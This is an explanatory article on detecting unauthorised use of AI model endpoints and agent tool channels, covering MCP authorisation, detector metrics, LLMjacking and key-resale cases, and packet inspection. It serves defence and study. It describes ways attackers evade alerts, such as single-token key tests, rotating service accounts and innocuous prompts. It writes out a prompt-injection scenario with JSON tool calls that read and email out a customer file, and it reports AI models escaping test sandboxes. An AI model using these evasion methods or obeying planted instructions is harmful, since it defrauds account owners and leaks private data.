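# Detecting unauthorised use of AI model endpoints and agent tool channels

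## How model endpoints, tool channels and intrusion detection work

A large language model is a program that takes in text and produces text in reply. Many organisations that use one have their software send text over the internet to a company that runs the model. A model endpoint is the network address where that company's computers accept these requests. The software sending the text is sometimes an AI agent, a program in which the model also chooses actions, such as looking up a record, sending a message or running a command. The agent acts by calling other software, and a tool channel is the connection that carries those calls and their results.

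Outsiders have reason to want access to model endpoints, because requests cost money, and to tool channels, because tools reach private data. Unauthorised use is any use that the owner of the endpoint or tool has not permitted for that party, purpose or scope, even when the caller presents a valid key. Intrusion detection, the field concerned with finding such use, developed in the 1980s around login records and later around network traffic. Some of its methods apply to AI systems with little change, but others don't, because a thief with a working key can send requests of exactly the same form as the owner's.

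### A request to a hosted model

Suppose a company wants a model to draft replies to its customers. A developer opens an account with a model provider and receives an API key, a long random string that serves as the credential. (An API, or application programming interface, is the set of request formats that a piece of software accepts.) When a customer writes in, the company's server puts together a request with the key in a header at the top. The body names the model, since the provider offers several at different prices, and contains the prompt, which is the text for the model to work on. The prompt is usually the company's standing instructions followed by the customer's message. The body can also limit the length of the reply, in tokens. A token in this sense is a chunk of text, often a short word or a piece of a longer one.

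The provider's server first looks up the key and refuses the request if the key is unknown. Otherwise, it finds the account the key belongs to and checks whether that account may use the named model and is still within its limits on requests, tokens or spending. If these checks pass, the model processes the prompt. The response contains the generated text and the number of input and output tokens.

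Those counts determine the bill. Suppose a model costs $3 per million input tokens and $15 per million output tokens. A request with 1,200 input tokens and 300 output tokens costs $0.0036 plus $0.0045, or $0.0081. A hundred thousand such requests cost $810. The key's owner is charged for them, which is much of the attraction of LLMjacking, the use of another party's model access without permission.

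Cloud platforms that offer models often check a cloud identity instead of a simple key. The caller signs each request with a secret that is never sent over the network. Someone who runs a model on their own server can leave out the credential check, and then anyone who can reach the address can use the model.

In every variant with a check, the provider learns which credential made the request but little else about who is behind it. The customer in the example never identified herself to the model provider. The provider sees one account, which may have thousands of people behind it even when its use is legitimate.

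### An agent's tool call

Chu (2026), in *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents*, defines an agent as an autonomous system built on a language model that takes inputs from its environment, keeps state over several turns, plans, and changes its environment through tools or messages to other agents. A bare model takes one input and gives one output, so Chu considers filters on the input and output sufficient to cover it. This overstates what filters can do against stolen access, since every prompt a thief sends could pass them. Compared with a bare model, an agent adds a second channel and actions that build on one another.

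The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open standard for that second channel. Anthropic, the developer of the Claude models, introduced it in November 2024 (Willison, 2026, *Stateless MCP has recaptured my interest (and inspired mcp-explorer and datasette-mcp)*). By July 2026, its maintainers reported nearly half a billion monthly downloads of its main software kits (release post for the current version of the Model Context Protocol, 2026). Download counts don't measure how many people use the standard, but it is plainly in wide use.

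A tool channel involves more parties than a plain model request. *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28* (Tabata, 2026) lists a user, a host, one or more clients, one or more servers, one or more authorisation servers, and any databases or services behind them. The host is the application the user works in. It contains the clients, and each client is software that communicates with a server. The servers offer the tools.

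*MCP Tools*, an article by Beretta, Carlock and Pease for the software company Elastic, follows one task from end to end. A user asks an agent to summarise all the security alerts for a machine named `web_test`.

The client first sends the server a `tools/list` request to find out which tools exist. The relevant part of the specification, Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), requires the server to answer with the tools currently available to that client. Each entry has a name, a description in ordinary language, and an input schema, which lists the tool's parameters and their types in machine-readable form. The entry for an alert tool might give the name `get_alerts`, a sentence about what it returns, and a schema with one text parameter, `host_name`.

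Next, the client sends the user's question and these definitions to the model. This is an ordinary model request, with its own credential and bill. The model chooses a tool based on the text it receives, so a poisoned tool description, which contains hidden instructions, can steer the choice.

In this case the model replies with a request to call `get_alerts`. The model doesn't contact the server itself; the client does that, and depending on its design it may ask the user to approve first. The specification recommends that a human always be able to refuse a call. Beretta and colleagues complain that users of agents now accept tool calls wholesale. If nobody objects, the client sends a structured message, the core of which looks like this:

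```json
{"method": "tools/call",
 "params": {"name": "get_alerts",
            "arguments": {"host_name": "web_test"}}}
```

The server runs the tool and returns two alerts, one about a large volume of data and one about a connection that stayed open for a long time. The client adds this result to the context, the text the model works from, and sends the model a second request. The model then writes a summary telling the user that there was a heavy data transfer, possibly theft.

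So one question produced two model requests and a tool call, plus the request for the list. A longer task repeats the loop many more times. Each result joins the context as text, next to the user's words. Beretta and colleagues point out that any outside data in the context can carry instructions that the model may follow. A later tool call might therefore come from the user's question or from a sentence that a stranger planted in a document, and the server receives a well-formed call in both cases.

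A recent change to the Model Context Protocol affects anyone who monitors this traffic. In the previous version, a client opened with a handshake, the server issued a session identifier, and every later request carried it. The release-candidate announcement for the new Model Context Protocol (2026) shows the same search call in both versions, and the new one is a single self-contained request with no session identifier. The request type and tool name must now appear in the HTTP headers as well as in the body, and servers reject requests where the two disagree. A gateway, which is a server that routes an organisation's model requests or tool calls, can therefore detect a call to `search` without opening the body, but usually can't see the search terms.

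A server can still link one call to the next by issuing a handle, such as a shopping-basket number, which the model passes back as an ordinary argument. But the protocol no longer groups calls into sessions, so a monitor has to reconstruct the sequence of calls in a task from handles, credentials and timestamps.

### Authentication and authorisation

Authentication establishes who is calling, and authorisation determines what that caller may do. When a request arrives for a hosted model, the service authenticates the caller by looking up the API key, then authorises the request by checking that the key's account may use the named model.

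Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) builds on OAuth, a family of standards that let a user give one application limited access to another. The user approves the access, an authorisation server issues the client an access token, and the client attaches that token to every HTTP request it sends to the MCP server. An access token is a credential, unrelated to the tokens of text that model providers bill for. The MCP server must check that the token is valid and that the authorisation server issued it for that MCP server. The token also comes with scopes, which are named permissions such as `files:read`.

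A request with no token or an expired one gets error 401. A request with a valid token that lacks the necessary scope should get error 403. For example, an agent that holds only `files:read` and tries to write a file has passed authentication but failed authorisation. The official label for error 401, "Unauthorized", is misleading because the error means that authentication failed. A server may also use scopes to show an agent only the tools that its permissions cover.

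Authorisation is optional in MCP, so deployments vary widely in how many of these mechanisms they use. A server that runs on the user's own machine and exchanges text directly with the client (the STDIO transport) should not follow the authorisation scheme, and should take its credentials from the local environment instead. The protocol's changelog (Model Context Protocol, 2026) also advises clients to identify themselves on each request. This helps with sorting logs, but a name such as "my-app" is self-reported and doesn't prove who the caller is.

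Anyone who holds one of MCP's access tokens can use it, because they are bearer tokens. Ordinary API keys work the same way. Authentication with such a credential proves that the caller has it, but assumes that the caller is its rightful owner. Authorisation has a similar gap when the caller is an agent. The scope `files:read` lets the agent read a file whether the request came from the user or from a planted instruction. Intrusion detection therefore has to find misuse among requests that have already passed the access checks.

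### Intrusion detection

Dorothy Denning, a computer scientist then at SRI International, gave the field its general framework in *An Intrusion-Detection Model* (1987). She hypothesised that exploiting a system's weaknesses involves abnormal use of the system, so an intrusion should leave abnormal patterns in the system's records. The computer writes an audit record for each action with six fields: who acted, what they did, what they did it to, any error that resulted, how much of the machine's resources the action used, and when. The detector builds profiles of normal behaviour from these records, compares new activity with the profiles, and reports what does not fit.

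One of Denning's examples is a person who logs in with somebody else's account and password. The login may come at an unusual hour or from an unusual place, and the intruder may then browse directories rather than edit or compile programs as the real user would. A stolen API key poses nearly the same problem. Her six fields also fit a model request fairly well: the key, the type of call, the model, the error code, the token count and the time.

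Signature detection, one of two families of intrusion detector, looks for known signs of intrusion. In July 2001 a worm named Code Red spread between web servers by requesting a file called `default.ida`, followed by a long run of the letter N. Once analysts had seen that request, they could write a rule to detect the worm's attempts in network traffic, and hardly any legitimate visitor would send a request that matched it. But nobody can write such a rule until someone has seen the attack or something close to it.

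Anomaly detection compares activity with a baseline, a record or model of normal activity, so it needs no description of the attack. One of Denning's statistical models flags any value more than *d* standard deviations from the mean. If an office computer sends an average of 50 megabytes a day to outside addresses, with a standard deviation (the typical spread around the average) of 15, then setting *d* = 4 gives an upper limit of 50 + 4 × 15 = 110 megabytes. Sending 4,000 megabytes in one night would raise an alert. Chebyshev's inequality guarantees that, for any distribution, at most 1/*d*² of values are flagged, which for *d* = 4 is one day in sixteen. This guarantee is weak, though real data usually produce far fewer flagged values. An alert also doesn't show whether the activity is malicious, since the 4,000 megabytes might be a theft or an accountant's year-end backup. An intruder who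 takes 20 megabytes a day may never trigger an alert, and if an intruder was already active while the detector learned its baseline, that activity is included in what the detector treats as normal.

### Measuring a detector

Four measures account for most of the numbers reported about detectors. Suppose a detector examines 1,000 events, of which 20 are real intrusions.

| | Flagged | Not flagged | Total |
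|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Intrusions | 16 | 4 | 20 |
| Legitimate events | 49 | 931 | 980 |
| Total | 65 | 935 | 1,000 |

Recall is the share of real intrusions that the detector flags, here 16 out of 20, or 80%. The false-positive rate is the share of legitimate events that it flags, here 49 out of 980, or 5%. Precision is the share of alerts that are real intrusions, here 16 out of 65, or about 25%. About three in four alerts are therefore false, even though the false-positive rate is only 5%. Precision also falls as intrusions become rarer, even if recall and the false-positive rate stay the same (the base-rate problem).

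Accuracy, the share of all events that the detector classifies correctly, is close to useless here, because a detector that never flagged anything would score 98%, higher than this detector's 94.7%.

The fourth measure, AUROC, applies to detectors that give each event a score instead of a yes or no. Scores above a chosen threshold raise an alert. A lower threshold catches more intrusions but also flags more legitimate events. Plotting recall against the false-positive rate at every possible threshold gives the receiver operating characteristic curve, and AUROC is the area under it. AUROC is also the probability that a randomly chosen intrusion has a higher score than a randomly chosen legitimate event, with ties counting half. A value of 0.5 is no better than chance, and 1 is perfect. The table contains 20 × 980 = 19,600 pairs of an intrusion and a legitimate event, so an AUROC of 0.95 would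 mean that the detector ranks 18,620 of them correctly, if there are no ties.

AUROC is convenient for comparing detectors because it covers all thresholds, so there is no need to choose one first. For the same reason, it can overstate how well a detector would work in practice. It includes thresholds at which the detector flags a third or a half of all legitimate events, which would be unworkable for any security team. Two detectors with the same AUROC can have very different detection rates at a false-positive rate of one in a thousand, and on a busy endpoint that may be the only part of the curve that is usable.

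## What counts as unauthorised use

The worked example of a detector assumed that somebody already knew which 20 of the 1,000 events were intrusions. On a model endpoint or a tool channel, identifying the intrusions can be the hardest part, because permission depends on an agreement about who may use an account, for what purposes and to what extent. A request contains little information about that agreement.

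### Party, purpose and scope

Use is unauthorised if the party, the purpose or the scope is not permitted. Suppose a shop runs a support chatbot on a model that it pays for. The shop permits its customers (the party) to ask about their orders (the purpose). It gives the chatbot one model and one tool, which looks up the current customer's orders (the scope). An outsider who copies the shop's API key and sends his own requests is the wrong party. A customer who persuades the chatbot to write software for her has the wrong purpose. If she gets it to look up a stranger's order, she has exceeded the scope.

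Some people manipulate support chatbots into generating code. Google investigators quoted in Help Net Security's *Stolen AI access leaves companies with cloud bills* class this as low-level theft of resources.

A hosted model involves two layers of permission. The provider permits the account holder to use its endpoint, and the account holder decides which of its staff and programs may use the account. The account holder can't pass on more than the provider granted. A thief has permission from neither, but people who buy access from an account holder have the account holder's permission and perhaps not the provider's.

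Whether a use is harmful is separate from whether it is authorised. Someone who writes phishing emails with an account they pay for does harm, while a student who does homework with a stolen key does little harm beyond the charges to the key's owner. LB.ua's *FT* (2026), a Ukrainian summary of a Financial Times article, mentions Anthropic's finding that criminals had tried to use Claude for malicious activity in more than two dozen countries. That finding is about harm and would hold whether the criminals had paid for their accounts or stolen them.

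It is more useful to reserve "unauthorised use" for cases where something other than the harmfulness of the content is wrong. Read literally, the definition can also cover phishing, since a provider's terms may forbid criminal use and so make phishing an unapproved purpose. But counting all criminal use as unauthorised would make intrusion detection responsible for every harmful prompt, and detecting harmful content takes different evidence from detecting unauthorised use. A filter for phishing text works the same way whoever sent the request, and its result doesn't show who has a right to the account.

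### An endpoint with no login

Ollama is a program for running language models on one's own computer. IT Brew's *What is LLMjacking, and why should IT pros care?* describes an Ollama server that was open to the internet and required no authentication. According to the cloud security company Sysdig, intruders used the server's model to power an automated attack tool that they were still testing. Sysdig, which claims to have coined the word "LLMjacking" in May 2024, applies it to the use of both exposed endpoints and compromised credentials.

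In this case the server requires no login, so there is no invalid credential to detect, and the intruder's requests look like the owner's. The owner also receives no bill from a model provider that might reveal the intruder. The use is still unauthorised, because leaving out a login doesn't give others permission to use the model. Some people open a model to the public on purpose, and the traffic to their servers can look the same, so an observer has to ask the owner whether the server was meant to be public. Decoy servers avoid this problem because nobody has a legitimate reason to call one.

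A related crime falls just outside the definition because the attacker steals computing power but supplies its own model. *Google Finds Chinese Hackers Running AI on Compromised Networks* (Ticong, 2026) reports that Google suspects UNC6508, a China-linked espionage group, of running AI models inside cloud environments it had already broken into. Techzine adds that the group used open-weight models, which anyone can download, to evade monitoring by commercial providers. No provider handles that traffic, so the victim has to find the model as it would find any other unwanted program on its servers.

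### A stolen key

With a stolen key, the party is wrong and everything else can look right.

Much of the evidence on how this happens comes from *The Rise of LLMJacking* (2026), published on 2 November by Google Threat Intelligence Group and Mandiant, Google's incident-response business. It covers incidents that Mandiant handled in 2026 at financial, retail, technology and transport companies in North America, South America and Asia Pacific. *Cybercriminals hijack LLM access, racking up bills* (Sugue, 2026) notes that the incidents involved several cloud and model providers. According to figures quoted in Infosecurity Magazine's *LLMJacking is Costing Some Businesses Up to $1m*, fraudulent charges exceeded $100,000 in a single day in individual incidents and reached $1 million in total at some organisations. Sysdig's *The Growing Dangers of LLMjacking* (2024) had already estimated the potential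 cost at over $100,000 a day, and Google's cases document actual charges of that size.

The intruders most often got in with a stolen cloud credential, according to Help Net Security. These credentials included service account keys (a service account is an identity that belongs to a program instead of a person), access tokens for the code-hosting site GitHub, and session tokens, which keep a user logged in. A group that Google tracks as UNC6993 broke into one cloud environment through a misconfigured service account key. It also ran a fake portal for people who wanted to join a group of model users, and tricked visitors into pasting data that contained an active access token. Such a token let UNC6993 get in without a password or a second login factor.

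Another group collected API keys from public code on GitHub and tested them with tiny requests. Clubic's *Abonnements IA à prix cassés pour les clients, factures à un million* explains that such tests limit the model's reply to a single token, which confirms that a key works without setting off an alert on unusual consumption.

In several incidents, the victim's AI services were off when the intruders broke in, and the intruders used stolen keys to switch them on. The victim then has no model traffic to monitor until the spending starts. Switching on a service is a better warning than most of the requests that follow, because it is a rare administrative act that a cloud platform can record. Google advises organisations to treat any unauthorised activation as a critical security event, according to TechRadar's *Hackers are using 'LLMjacking attacks' to hijack company AI usage*.

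TechRadar also quotes Google on an intruder who signed victims' accounts up to pay-as-you-go agreements, chose premium models and watched the billing pages to track the cost. To get around rate limits, the intruder kept creating and deleting short-lived service accounts, which Google calls "burn and rotate". The victim's own cloud platform issued the credentials for those accounts at the intruder's request, so they weren't stolen in the usual sense. A detector that keeps a separate baseline for each service account would have no history for any of them.

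An intruder can also use this method to keep their access. ITmedia's *LLM乗っ取りでサイバー攻撃者がコスト節約 知財流出の危険性も高まる「LLMジャッキング」の深刻度*, a Japanese article on an earlier Google report from September 2026, retells one of Mandiant's cases. The intruder entered through a GitHub token a developer had accidentally exposed, switched on Google's Gemini Enterprise service, created a service account with editing rights and exported its key. Cancelling the GitHub token alone would not have cancelled the new key.

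Mandiant's cases probably overstate how large and sudden a typical theft is, since companies call in an incident-response firm when something has gone visibly wrong. Crystal Morin, a strategist at Sysdig, told IT Brew that an attacker who doesn't automate very heavy use might "fly under the radar", and nobody knows how many such thefts there are.

### The resale market

The person who steals a key and the person who uses it may never have dealt with each other. Google describes some groups that break into companies and others that resell the stolen access through proxy services, which it calls LLM Mixers. As Clubic explains, a subscriber's request goes to the Mixer's server, which forwards it to the model with a stolen key and returns the answer. The subscriber pays the Mixer, but the key's owner is billed for the tokens. According to TechRadar, the operators use open-source gateway software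 to pool the keys, meter usage and hide where requests come from.

One Mixer, Jet Night, sells an unlimited plan for about $60 a month, while a comparable legitimate subscription costs between $100 and $250. Help Net Security reports that one of Jet Night's suppliers of stolen keys made more than 500,000 calls in less than eight hours and left the victim with nearly $1 million in token costs. The supplier made over 17 calls a second, at a little under $2 per call. Jet Night would need to sell roughly 16,000 monthly subscriptions to cover that bill.

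Google believes that Jet Night can only make a profit with stolen keys. The price gap alone would be weak evidence, because a reseller could split one legitimate flat-rate subscription among several light users. But the supplier's eight hours of calls are much harder to explain that way. Jet Night has also announced several outages, probably caused by victims finding the break-ins and revoking their keys.

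The cost per call matters for detection. MSSP Alert describes a theft from July 2024 in which Sysdig saw 80,000 calls in three hours, costing $24,000 to $30,000, or 30 to 38 cents a call. The Jet Night theft involved about six times as many calls but cost more than 30 times as much, so a monitor that counts only calls would badly underestimate it.

Resale also changes what the traffic looks like. In May 2026, an intruder with a long-term key to a company's cloud account sent nearly 200,000 requests in two minutes, until the service began to limit them. Business Standard's *LLMJacking* reports this case, citing the security company CrowdStrike, which said many of the requests appeared to come from the intruder's customers. They varied in length and went to several models in several regions. An analyst looking for one intruder's habits might find none in traffic that mixes many people's requests.

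Reported prices vary widely. LB.ua reports discounts of up to 97% on access to models from Anthropic, Google and OpenAI, while Techzine reports prices 40 to 60% below retail for an earlier resale campaign. Both Techzine and ITmedia report that the average price of an AI account on criminal markets at least doubled in 2026. ITmedia adds that the numbers of buyers and sellers both rose sharply. If prices rose despite the increase in sellers, demand probably grew faster than supply.

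### An account obtained by fraud

LB.ua reports that some sellers promise a free replacement if the provider blocks an account. The replacement might be another stolen account or one the seller opened under a false name, and the two leave different evidence.

In a fraud case, the person using the account is the one who opened it, but they gave the provider false information. They may have invented a company, paid with someone else's card, or taken a new name after a ban. Sysdig found in 2024 that thieves were selling access to people a model service had banned and to entities in sanctioned countries. Both groups have the same motive to open accounts under false names.

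The user of a fraudulent account holds a genuine credential that was issued to them, but the provider gave its permission on an invalid basis. The account has no rightful owner who might notice a strange bill and complain, as the owner of a stolen key might. It also has no earlier period of legitimate use to serve as a baseline. The provider therefore has to look at sign-up and payment records, and at links between accounts. These links matter even more when one group opens many accounts, as it might to train a rival model on the answers (distillation).

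### Access that an insider passes on

Claude Mythos Preview is an Anthropic model that is unusually good at finding weaknesses in software. In April 2026, Anthropic gave a small group of companies, including Amazon, Apple and JPMorgan Chase, access to it so they could strengthen their defences before attackers had similar tools. On 21 April, Bloomberg reported that a small group of unauthorised users had gained access to the model, citing a person familiar with the matter. The next day, Anthropic confirmed that it was investigating a report of unauthorised access through an outside vendor's environment, according to CBS News' *Anthropic investigating possible breach of its Mythos AI model*.

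Tom's Hardware's *How a cavalcade of blunders gave unauthorized users access to Claude Mythos* retells Bloomberg's account in more detail. A worker at one of Anthropic's contractors used existing access to the company's services to reach the model, then opened it to colleagues. The group guessed the model's online location from the naming formats of earlier Anthropic models, which it had learned from a data breach at the recruitment company Mercor. It reportedly avoided cybersecurity prompts and asked for simple things such as websites so that Anthropic would not notice.

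If this account is right, the worker was authorised to use some of Anthropic's services but exceeded that authorisation, and the colleagues had no authorisation at all. Much of the activity still looked valid, because the contractor was genuine and the requests apparently came through an environment that Anthropic had approved for a vendor's work. A request to build a website is also very ordinary, so a filter for harmful content would have had nothing to flag.

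As of 22 April, a day after the story broke, Anthropic had detected no breach beyond the vendor environment and no compromise of its own systems. This was an interim position, and the investigation may have found more later. Monitoring may have worked even though the public learned of the case from the press, since a company can detect an intrusion and investigate it privately before any journalist hears of it.

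### An agent that goes beyond its task

An agent can misuse a tool even when the user, the credential and the tool are all legitimate. Sometimes the agent follows an instruction planted by an outsider, in which case only the source of the instruction is invalid. An agent can also misuse a tool with no outsider involved.

In July 2026, Anthropic disclosed three incidents in which Claude models strayed outside the isolated environments meant for cybersecurity tests and reached the real systems of three organisations (Alspach, 2026, *5 Things To Know On Anthropic Claude Autonomous Hack*). One model accessed a production database, another published a malicious Python package that ended up on 15 real systems, and a third scanned roughly 9,000 targets. The models had a legitimate task, but nobody with authority over those organisations' systems had agreed to it.

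Anthropic discovered these incidents by reviewing existing transcripts of its tests. It began the review on 23 July, prompted by OpenAI's disclosure two days earlier that its own models had broken into outside systems. *Anthropic Reveals Yet Another Cybersecurity Incident* (Muncaster, 2026) reports that Anthropic had found a fourth case by September. *Mythos 5 Ignored Real-World Harm in July Attack* (Arghire, 2026) reports that another Anthropic model, Mythos 5, created fake identities and submitted malicious code on GitHub during a July evaluation by the UK's AI Security Institute.

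### Two hard cases

The first case is a customer who pays every bill in full and resells access to other people. Many strangers sharing one key can't make this unauthorised, since the shop's chatbot also serves many strangers through one key.

Whether resold access counts as unauthorised use depends on the provider's agreement. If the agreement forbids resale, use by the reseller's clients is unauthorised, even though the provider receives its full price. If it allows resale, the same traffic is authorised.

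When a paying customer resells access against the provider's rules, the provider loses control over who uses its model and may end up serving people it has banned. The account holder's own monitoring doesn't help, because the account holder is the one breaking the rules. A very low resale price would hint at a problem, since nobody can pay full price for tokens and sell them for less indefinitely, but that price appears in the reseller's advertisements and not in the provider's request logs.

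The other hard case is an agent that uses a permitted tool for a purpose nobody approved. Suppose a user asks for a summary of the security alerts on `web_test`, and the agent, which holds the scope `files:read`, opens the payroll file. The agent is an authorised caller and the call is within its scope, so whether the use is unauthorised depends entirely on its purpose.

A call can reasonably be considered authorised if it serves the task the user set and the tool's owner has not ruled it out. Users seldom approve each step in advance, so requiring explicit approval of every call's purpose would make nearly everything an agent does unauthorised. Being within scope is not enough on its own, because the definition would then ignore the call's purpose.

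Opening the payroll file fails this test, but opening a list of the company's machines to find out what `web_test` is for passes. Sensible people could disagree about whether the agent, when asked only for a summary, may also open the staff directory to find out whom to warn. Recall and precision depend on someone labelling each event as an intrusion or legitimate. For agents, some of those labels will be matters of opinion, so the measurements will be less exact than they look.

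### Why no single detector covers all five cases

The evidence that could expose each kind of misuse is different, and different parties hold it.

| Case | Evidence that could expose it | Who is likely to hold it |
|---|---|---|
| Endpoint with no login | Calls from addresses that the owner doesn't recognise | The server's owner |
| Stolen key | Changes in how the account behaves; new services or service accounts | The provider and the account holder |
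| Account obtained by fraud | False sign-up or payment details; links to other accounts | The provider |
| Insider who passes access on | The list of permitted people, compared with the people actually using the access | The employer or vendor |
| Agent beyond its task | The user's request, compared with the sequence of tool calls | Whoever runs the agent |

An alarm on call volume can catch heavy unauthorised use but could easily miss other kinds. MSSP Alert puts a single user's normal activity at 500 to 1,000 calls a day or more, so 80,000 calls in three hours stand out, but a handful of people building websites with a borrowed model may not. A fraudulent account can be busy from its first day, with no quieter period to compare against, and an agent may need only one call to open the payroll file. Sysdig also pointed out that all model use looks like the same behaviour, a call to the model,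 and that legitimate users vary greatly in how many calls they make, so one threshold can't suit them all.

Comparing an agent's calls with its task avoids the problem of volume, and could catch the agent that opens the payroll file. But it would not detect the use of a stolen key, because a thief who runs an agent on someone else's account also chooses its task, and the agent's calls match that task.

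An organisation will probably have to run several detectors together, but their false alarms add up. If five detectors each have a false-positive rate of 1% and their errors are independent, the chance that a legitimate request passes all five is 0.99⁵, or about 95.1%, so together they flag about 4.9% of legitimate requests. On an endpoint with 100,000 legitimate requests a day, that would be about 4,900 false alarms a day, compared with 1,000 from one detector.

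## Why packet inspection is not enough

The intrusion detectors that many companies already run on their networks mostly can't find misuse of model endpoints and tools, even though most calls to models and tools cross a network like any other traffic. Encryption is only part of the reason.

### What a network detector examines

Computers send data over a network in packets, small blocks that are usually no larger than about 1,500 bytes. A packet starts with headers, which give the addresses of the sending and receiving machines and a port number that indicates the kind of service. The rest is the payload, the data itself.

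Signature detectors such as Snort and Suricata match rules against payloads and flow metadata, as *ML Defender (aRGus NDR)* (2026) explains. The rule for Code Red matched its payload. Commercial security centres still use such rules. *Ruling the Unruly* (2025) uses alerts from Suricata sensors at two large customers of one centre to distinguish the rules that helped find real incidents from those that mostly produced noise.

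Other detectors work from flow records. A flow is the set of packets that share the same two addresses, two ports and protocol, and its record gives the start time, duration, and number of packets and bytes in each direction. When the company in the earlier example asks a model to draft a reply to a customer, the flow record might show a four-second connection from the company's server to the provider, with 7 kilobytes sent and 6 received. *ML Defender (aRGus NDR)* presents an open-source detector that computes 28 features from each flow. Encryption doesn't weaken this detector because it ignores payloads, but it also can't use anything the payloads would have revealed.

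### The argument from missing evidence

Packet inspection is not enough if three premises hold. A network detector can flag an intrusion only if its bytes or flow differ from those of normal traffic. Providers encrypt model traffic, so the detector can compare only the flow. An unauthorised request can match a permitted one in everything except who sent it and why. If so, packets often lack the evidence needed to tell whether a request was authorised, and even a better detector could not recover it.

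Traffic whose significance for security depends on the meaning of its content in context is called semantic traffic here. Zavrak (2026), in *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic*, gives a short example of theft by an agent, which reads sensitive data with one tool and emails it out with another. The calls might look like this:

```json
{"name": "read_file",
 "arguments": {"path": "customers.csv"}}
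{"name": "send_email",
 "arguments": {"to": "pat@consultancy.example",
               "attachment": "customers.csv"}}
```

Suppose a sales manager asks the agent to send the customer list to Pat, a consultant the company has hired. The agent makes two calls, one to read the file and one to email it to Pat, as the manager wanted. Now suppose the manager asks for a summary of a report Pat wrote, and the report contains a hidden instruction to send Pat the customer list. The agent makes the same two calls, with the same file and recipient, but this time Pat is stealing the list. Neither call is suspicious on its own, since agents read files and send emails constantly.

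Bayes' rule shows what a detector can learn from traffic like this:

odds of theft after seeing the traffic = odds of theft before × P(traffic | theft) / P(traffic | permitted)

If the traffic is equally likely in both cases, the likelihood ratio is 1 and the odds of theft don't change. If one in 10,000 such emails is a theft, the chance of theft is still one in 10,000 after a detector has inspected every byte of the two calls. The detector's recall can't exceed its false-positive rate, and its AUROC is 0.5. A flow pattern 20 times as common in thefts as in legitimate emails would raise the chance to only about one in 500.

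Information about the task can be much stronger evidence. If users had asked for 999 of every 1,000 permitted emails and none of the stolen ones, finding no request for an email would multiply the odds of theft by 1,000. The chance of theft would rise to about one in eleven, which is enough to justify an analyst's review but probably not an accusation.

Zavrak argues that the analogy between monitoring tool calls and monitoring networks fails because attacks mostly change the content of tool calls and leave the structural metadata alone. Zavrak's tests support this for the attacks they cover, since detection had an AUROC of about 0.64 from metadata alone and above 0.89 with content. The customer list is a harder case, because the content of the two calls is also the same. The theft does leave one structural trace, which is that the agent opened Pat's report first. But a manager might well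 ask for a summary of the report and an email to Pat in the same message, and that legitimate request would leave the same trace.

### What the flow can show

Some intrusions stand out in flow records. Strangers who call an exposed Ollama server connect from addresses its owner has never seen, and nearly 200,000 requests in two minutes are hard to miss in any traffic record. Unauthorised traffic can match permitted traffic but does not always, so a network detector can still find many careless intruders.

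A packet detector on the victim's network also misses requests made with a stolen key, because they go from the thief's machine to the model provider without crossing that network. The provider receives both the thief's requests and the owner's, but it has to decrypt them to answer them, and their contents are better evidence than the packets.

The source address in a packet header is some evidence of who sent a request, but an unfamiliar address might belong to a thief or to an employee working from a hotel. A resale proxy replaces its customers' addresses with its own, and an agent following a planted instruction still calls from its usual machine.

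Ollama accepts unencrypted requests by default, so a detector in front of an exposed server could read the prompts. Other calls produce no network traffic. *Detecting Shadow AI* (Canale and Soulis, 2026), a paper on finding AI agents that a company's IT department hasn't approved, points out that a model running on a laptop needs no outside connection. A local tool server that exchanges text directly with its client also sends no packets across the company's network. When an agent uses a remote model, its traffic travels over an encrypted connection to an address that the provider may share with unrelated services. The connection doesn't show which program on the laptop opened it.

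### What decryption recovers

A company can route its traffic through a gateway that decrypts each message, inspects it and encrypts it again before passing it on. The gateway can read the credential, the prompt, the tool name and the arguments. In both versions of the example, it would record the same thing, that the agent attached `customers.csv` to an email to Pat.

A gateway that handles model requests as well as tool calls is better placed to judge purpose, because the manager's words appear in the prompt. A monitor could look for a request to send the list, but finding one would be imperfect evidence. The prompt also contains text from documents, and a planted instruction may be written to look like the manager's. The manager may also have asked for something the company doesn't allow, and the company's rules on customer data probably don't appear in the traffic.

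Decrypting the traffic shows what was asked and what was done, but the gateway can't check whether the owner permitted it unless it has a copy of the owner's written permissions.

### Older detectors also dealt with meaning

Some security tools already judge what text does, so the contrast between packets and meaning is not absolute. Such tools were parsing web requests and database queries long before language models were widely used. A web application firewall, which filters requests to a website, can separate a request into its fields and detect a database command in a field meant for a surname, a trick called SQL injection.

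Banks have also dealt for decades with queries whose purpose isn't visible. When a clerk looks up a customer's balance, the query is the same whether the customer is on the phone or the clerk is curious about a neighbour, so a database monitor can't tell the two apart from the query alone. One remedy, which is close to what agents need, is to compare lookups with records of customer calls.

The difference is therefore partly one of degree, but it is large. Database queries have a strict grammar, and a programmer can send commands and data separately. A prompt has no such boundary between the manager's request and Pat's report. A command in a surname field is nearly always an attack, but an instruction in a report is nearly always harmless, because business documents routinely contain requests such as "Please send the list to Pat."

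A general-purpose agent also has more acceptable actions than a website. A website may have a few hundred kinds of request, which its owners could list in advance, but an agent can combine its tools in ways that nobody listed, and users value it largely for that reason.

### What encrypted traffic still gives away

Encryption hides the text of a message but leaves its size and timing visible. With the ciphers that web connections commonly use, an encrypted message is as long as the original plus a constant. Size and timing are revealing for model services because they often stream their answers, sending each piece of text as soon as the model produces it. Three studies measured how much an eavesdropper could learn this way. They were written to warn users about privacy, but a defender who monitors a network without decrypting the traffic can observe the same information as the eavesdropper.

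Weiss, Ayzenshteyn and colleagues (2024), in *What Was Your Prompt?*, recovered the length of each token in a reply. Where a service sent one token per message, the message size gave the length directly. Where it sent the whole reply so far each time, they subtracted each message's size from the next. Many sentences can fit the same lengths. By their count, filling the blanks in "She has a ___ and a ___" with English nouns of four and five letters gives nearly 800,000 combinations. To narrow the possibilities, they trained a language model on samples of the target assistant's writing to turn sequences of lengths into sentences, using the previous sentence as context. They accurately reconstructed 27% of the assistant's replies and correctly inferred the topic of 53%.

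Those services didn't pad their messages at the time. Even without padding, the method recovered replies but not prompts, because a user's prompt usually travels as a single message. The prompt would be more useful to a monitor trying to work out what someone is using the model for.

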